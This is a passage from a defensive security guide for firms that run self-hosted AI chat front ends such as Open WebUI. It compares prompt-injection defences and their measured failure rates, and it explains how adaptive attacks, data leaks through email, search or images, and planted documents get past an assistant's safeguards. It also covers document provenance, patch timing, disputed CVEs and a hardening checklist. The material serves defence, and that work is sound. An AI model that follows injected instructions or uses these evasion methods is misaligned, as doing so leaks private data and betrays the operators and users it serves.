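| Marking retrieved text (Hines and colleagues) | From over 50% to under 2% | Little |
| Training to rank instructions (*SecAlign*) | To under 10% | Little |
| Detection filter (*AgentDojo*) | From about half to 8% | Completed tasks fell from 69% to about 41% |
| Choosing tools before reading documents (*AgentDojo*) | From about half to about 7% | No loss |

Most of these tests used a fixed set of attacks written before the defence existed. In *The Attacker Moves Second*, published in October 2025, Nasr, Carlini and colleagues instead adapted their attacks to each of 12 defences, using automated search and human testers to revise the attack text after seeing each result. In the original tests of most of these defences, attacks had success rates near zero. The adaptive attacks succeeded more than 90% of the time against most of them, including defences based on marking, training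 and filters.

An outsider who sends the firm one brochure can't watch its chat page and adjust the text. But the front end is open source, and the attacker may be able to use the same model, so they can refine the attack on their own copy until it works there. They would still have to guess the firm's settings and what other documents it has in its collection. The actual protection probably lies between the two sets of results, closer to the better set for mass-produced attacks and closer to the worse set for attacks aimed at this firm.

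Even defences that test well let some attacks through, and a 2% success rate still gives an attacker who makes 200 different attempts a 98% chance of succeeding at least once. Hashemi Natanzi and Tang warn that attackers can also evade filters by changing the formatting, alphabet or language of an attack while keeping its meaning. The Copilot attack exploited this weakness.

An operator can apply marking today by editing the template that inserts retrieved text, with almost no effort or expense. The model's maker controls training, so the operator can only choose which model to use. A filter can run in a model gateway or as an Open WebUI Function, but a Function from a stranger is code with access to the whole front end, so installing one to stop misleading documents could make the firm less safe.

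### Keeping untrusted text away from decisions

Another kind of defence limits what the model can do when it does obey the brochure. The last row of the table shows a simple version. The model chooses its tools after seeing only the user's request, and the application removes the rest. Summarising the brochure for an employee doesn't require an email tool, so the model has no means of obeying an instruction to send an email. The method fails when it's impossible to predict which tools a task will need. It also fails when the attack needs only the permitted tools, as 17% of the *AgentDojo* attacks did.

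A more thorough design is CaMeL, from *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design*, published in 2025 by Debenedetti, Shumailov and colleagues. Suppose the employee asks the assistant to find the hotel's address in its last letter and send it to her manager. CaMeL would divide the work like this:

1. A model that sees only her request writes a short program: find the letter, extract the address, send it to the manager.
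2. A second model, which has no tools, reads the letter and returns the address.
3. Ordinary code runs the program and records where each value came from.
4. Before sending anything, the code checks a rule, for example that text from private files may go only to colleagues.

An instruction in the letter can corrupt the extracted address, but it can't add a step to the program or change the recipient. With these guarantees, CaMeL completed 77% of the *AgentDojo* tasks, compared with 84% for an undefended system. Ordinary code enforces the rules, so an attacker can't gain new permissions by finding better wording. The protection depends on someone writing good rules, and it doesn't cover false facts. If the brochure falsely claims that the firm refunds 250 euros a night, CaMeL will still pass that claim on to the employee.

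None of the front ends offers CaMeL as a setting, as far as their documentation shows. An operator can get part of the benefit by creating two assistants, one that reads outside documents but has no tools, and one that has tools but reads only material that staff wrote. Switching between them may be tedious, and an employee can still paste an outside document into the assistant that has tools.

Where one assistant must do both jobs, a person should approve each action that sends, deletes or pays. The approval request has to show the recipient and the complete content, because an employee who sees only "Send email?" will soon click yes from habit. Web search needs the same caution as email, because a model that has read the salary file could put a salary in its search terms, and the search company or the owner of a fetched page would receive it. Blocking images from outside websites closes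 a similar leak through the chat page.

### Looking after the documents

Design changes inside the model's software do little about a false claim, so the firm has to control what enters the collection. Hashemi Natanzi and Tang list source allowlists and provenance labels among the defences against people who write outside content. An allowlist names the sources that staff may add without asking, such as the firm's own policies. A provenance record tells a later reader where a document came from:

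```
Document:      hotel-brochure-2026.pdf
Written by:    Hotel in Graz (outside the firm)
Uploaded by:   Office manager, 4 March 2026
Reviewed by:   Travel coordinator, 5 March 2026
Use for:       Hotel facilities and prices
Do not use for: What the firm refunds
Review again:  March 2027
```

The provenance record is useful only if the software acts on it. If the firm keeps outside documents in a separate collection, an assistant for refund questions can search only the policies, so it won't retrieve the brochure. If the software only adds a label beside the passage, the label may not affect the model's answer. Provenance also doesn't establish truth, since a digital signature can prove that the hotel wrote the brochure but not that the brochure is accurate.

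Reviewers need to read the extracted text, since the page they see may hide a paragraph or display a number differently. Open WebUI lets a user hover over a highlight in a document preview to see the passage the model received. For web pages and some other files, the retrieved text opens in its own window. These views help most when someone wants to trace a strange answer to its source.

There is little evidence on how well any of this works in practice. The poisoning experiments measured attacks on collections that nobody was reviewing, and no published test seems to show how often an office worker spots a planted paragraph among genuine ones. Hashemi Natanzi and Tang still list retrieval that tracks provenance as an open research problem. The strongest argument again rests on how the system is structured, because a document that the assistant never searches can't mislead it.

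If a false document does get in, deleting the uploaded file may not be enough. An operator can remove it in this order:

1. Save a copy of the file, the upload record and the affected answers as evidence.
2. Delete the file through the front end. Open WebUI's file manager, under Settings and then Data Controls, also removes the file's embeddings.
3. Search for a distinctive phrase from the text, in case the same passage is in another file or in a saved memory.
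4. Repeat the question that produced the wrong answer, in a new chat, and check the sources.
5. Tell the people who received the wrong answer, since their old chats still contain it.

Open WebUI also has an experimental option to search an external vector database instead of its own. Operators who use this option should delete the chunks from that database too. Restoring an old backup can bring the planted text back, so the evidence file should note which backups contain it.

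### How quickly do fixes arrive?

Open WebUI tells people who report flaws to expect review and a fix to take several weeks, citing a very high number of reports. It doesn't pay them bounties or accept publication deadlines from them. It issued an incomplete patch for the flaw involving hostile model servers after 11 days, and an advisory for the flaw in knowledge base search after 45 days. The company behind Dify never responded to the report of its template flaw, according to the public record.

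These cases are not a random sample, so they can't establish an average time to a fix. But they show that an operator can't count on a fix within a week, which is one more reason to have the VPN and firewall in place beforehand.

Open WebUI develops in public, so a security fix can appear in its development branch, where attackers can read it, before the release that contains it. Wiz reports that attackers often turn such fixes into working attacks before anyone has assigned a CVE number. Open WebUI has seen people monitor its public changes automatically and send back the flaws as new reports, and attackers could run the same kind of monitor without reporting what they find.

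An operator who updates a week after each release runs known-vulnerable code for 7 days, compared with about 35 days for one who waits about four weeks for the advisory and then takes a week to update. Waiting can avoid flaws introduced by a new release, such as the one 0.10.0 introduced with formulas, but for a server on the internet the risk of waiting is greater. A firm behind a VPN can reasonably take a few days to back up the database and test the release on a copy.

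Users of Open WebUI's free edition can get security fixes only by upgrading to new versions, because the project supports only its main branch. Its paid enterprise plans offer long-term support. Between the advisory of May 10, 2026 and the end of September, at least four releases (0.9.6, 0.10.0, 0.11.0 and 0.11.1) fixed flaws described in the earlier chapters. An operator who updates twice a year will usually be running a version with a publicly disclosed vulnerability.

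### What counts as a flaw?

On October 9, 2025, the Zero Day Initiative (ZDI) reported that Open WebUI transmitted passwords in readable form, and Open WebUI closed the report the next day. According to the timeline in ZDI's *(0Day) Open WebUI Cleartext Transmission of Credentials Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2026), ZDI asked for the reason five days later, asked about a fix in November, and said in December that it would publish. It published the advisory as ZDI-26-033 on January 9, 2026. The only remedy the advisory offered was to restrict interaction with the product.

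The report was correct that plain HTTP exposes passwords to anyone who can watch the traffic. But in *CVE-2026-0767* (2026), Open WebUI replies that this is true of every web application served over HTTP. The reverse proxy normally handles encryption, and no change to the chat software would supply the operator's certificate.

As in the dispute about Tools, Open WebUI admits that it should have explained in writing why it closed the report. It filed a formal dispute on May 4, 2026. The Zero Day Initiative agreed on July 8 but did not withdraw the record until September 2. By then, the record had been public for 222 days, 56 of them after both sides agreed that it was wrong. INCIBE's *CVE-2026-0767* (2026) now gives the behaviour of plain HTTP as the reason for the rejection.

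The withdrawal was right because there was nothing to patch, but operators could wrongly take it to mean that there was nothing to do. Many of the services that Hou and colleagues found on the internet used plain HTTP, and turning on encryption removes the exposure completely. Saying so in October 2025 might have saved everyone most of a year.

LibreChat's maintainer closed a report about the application's shared secret because of protections that turned out to have gaps. Neither a closed report nor a CVE number, then, settles whether a flaw is real. An operator has to check what an attacker would need and whether the installation provides it.

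A scanner can bury a real flaw among false alarms if it relies on a vulnerability database that still lists withdrawn CVEs as active. By October 30, 2026, issuers had withdrawn 26 CVEs against Open WebUI. Open WebUI's *Rejected CVEs in Vulnerability Databases* (2026) reports that Positive Technologies' database still showed all 26 as active on that date, and Vulmon's showed 20 of them. A CVE's entry at cve.org shows whether it has been withdrawn.

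### Has AI raised the number of reports?

AI tools find real flaws in these programs. An AI agent discovered the Open WebUI flaw that let a webhook's profile picture carry a script. Open WebUI asks people who report flaws to disclose whether they used AI to find the flaw, write the report or demonstrate the attack, and it handles AI-assisted reports like any others.

AI has probably contributed to the number of advisories, but it's unclear how much. One public list has 89 Open WebUI advisories from 2026, including 19 from two days in September. The project hasn't published how many reporters disclosed AI help, so the advisories found with AI can't be separated from those found without it. The 2026 count also includes the upload flaw that KoreLogic reported in 2024, because advisories are counted by publication date. More users, more features and a more systematic publication policy would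 also raise the count.

Whatever the answer, good reports wait longer if a maintainer receives more than a small team can read. Attackers' tools also improve along with researchers' tools.

### What to do first

A single user who runs a front end on their own computer should make it reachable only from that machine and update it regularly. Those two steps remove nearly all the attacks by strangers and colleagues. The remaining risk comes from plugins, model files, web pages and documents that other people wrote. The user should read a plugin's source before installing it, or do without the plugin, and should keep tools that can send email or run commands out of chats about outside documents. An elaborate permission system would add little protection.

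For a team such as the engineering firm, the order might be:

1. Put the front end behind a VPN or an authenticating proxy with encryption, and close registration.
2. Give the databases and model backend no public port, and replace every default secret.
3. Keep two administrators with separate everyday accounts, and switch plugins off unless someone needs them.
4. Subscribe to release notices and install updates within days.
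5. Block the server's access to internal addresses it doesn't need.
6. Keep outside documents in their own collection, away from policies and from assistants with tools.

The first four steps come before any prompt-injection filter because they address the attacks that intruders are known to have carried out. If a firm's assistant already reads incoming email and can act on it, the firm should do the sixth step first, or remove the assistant's tools until the other steps are done.

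Anyone can use a public assistant, so the operator should assume that visitors will eventually read its system prompt and every document it can search. Both should contain only material that the firm would publish anyway. The assistant should run on a separate server from the staff's chats, with its own provider key and a spending limit on that key. The administration page should be reachable only through the VPN. Limits on requests per visitor slow down both extraction and the repeated trials that adaptive attacks require. The assistant should have no tool that changes anything or looks up private records, unless ordinary code checks the visitor's identity first. If the operator can't install a security release within a day or two, it is safer to take the chat box offline until someone can.
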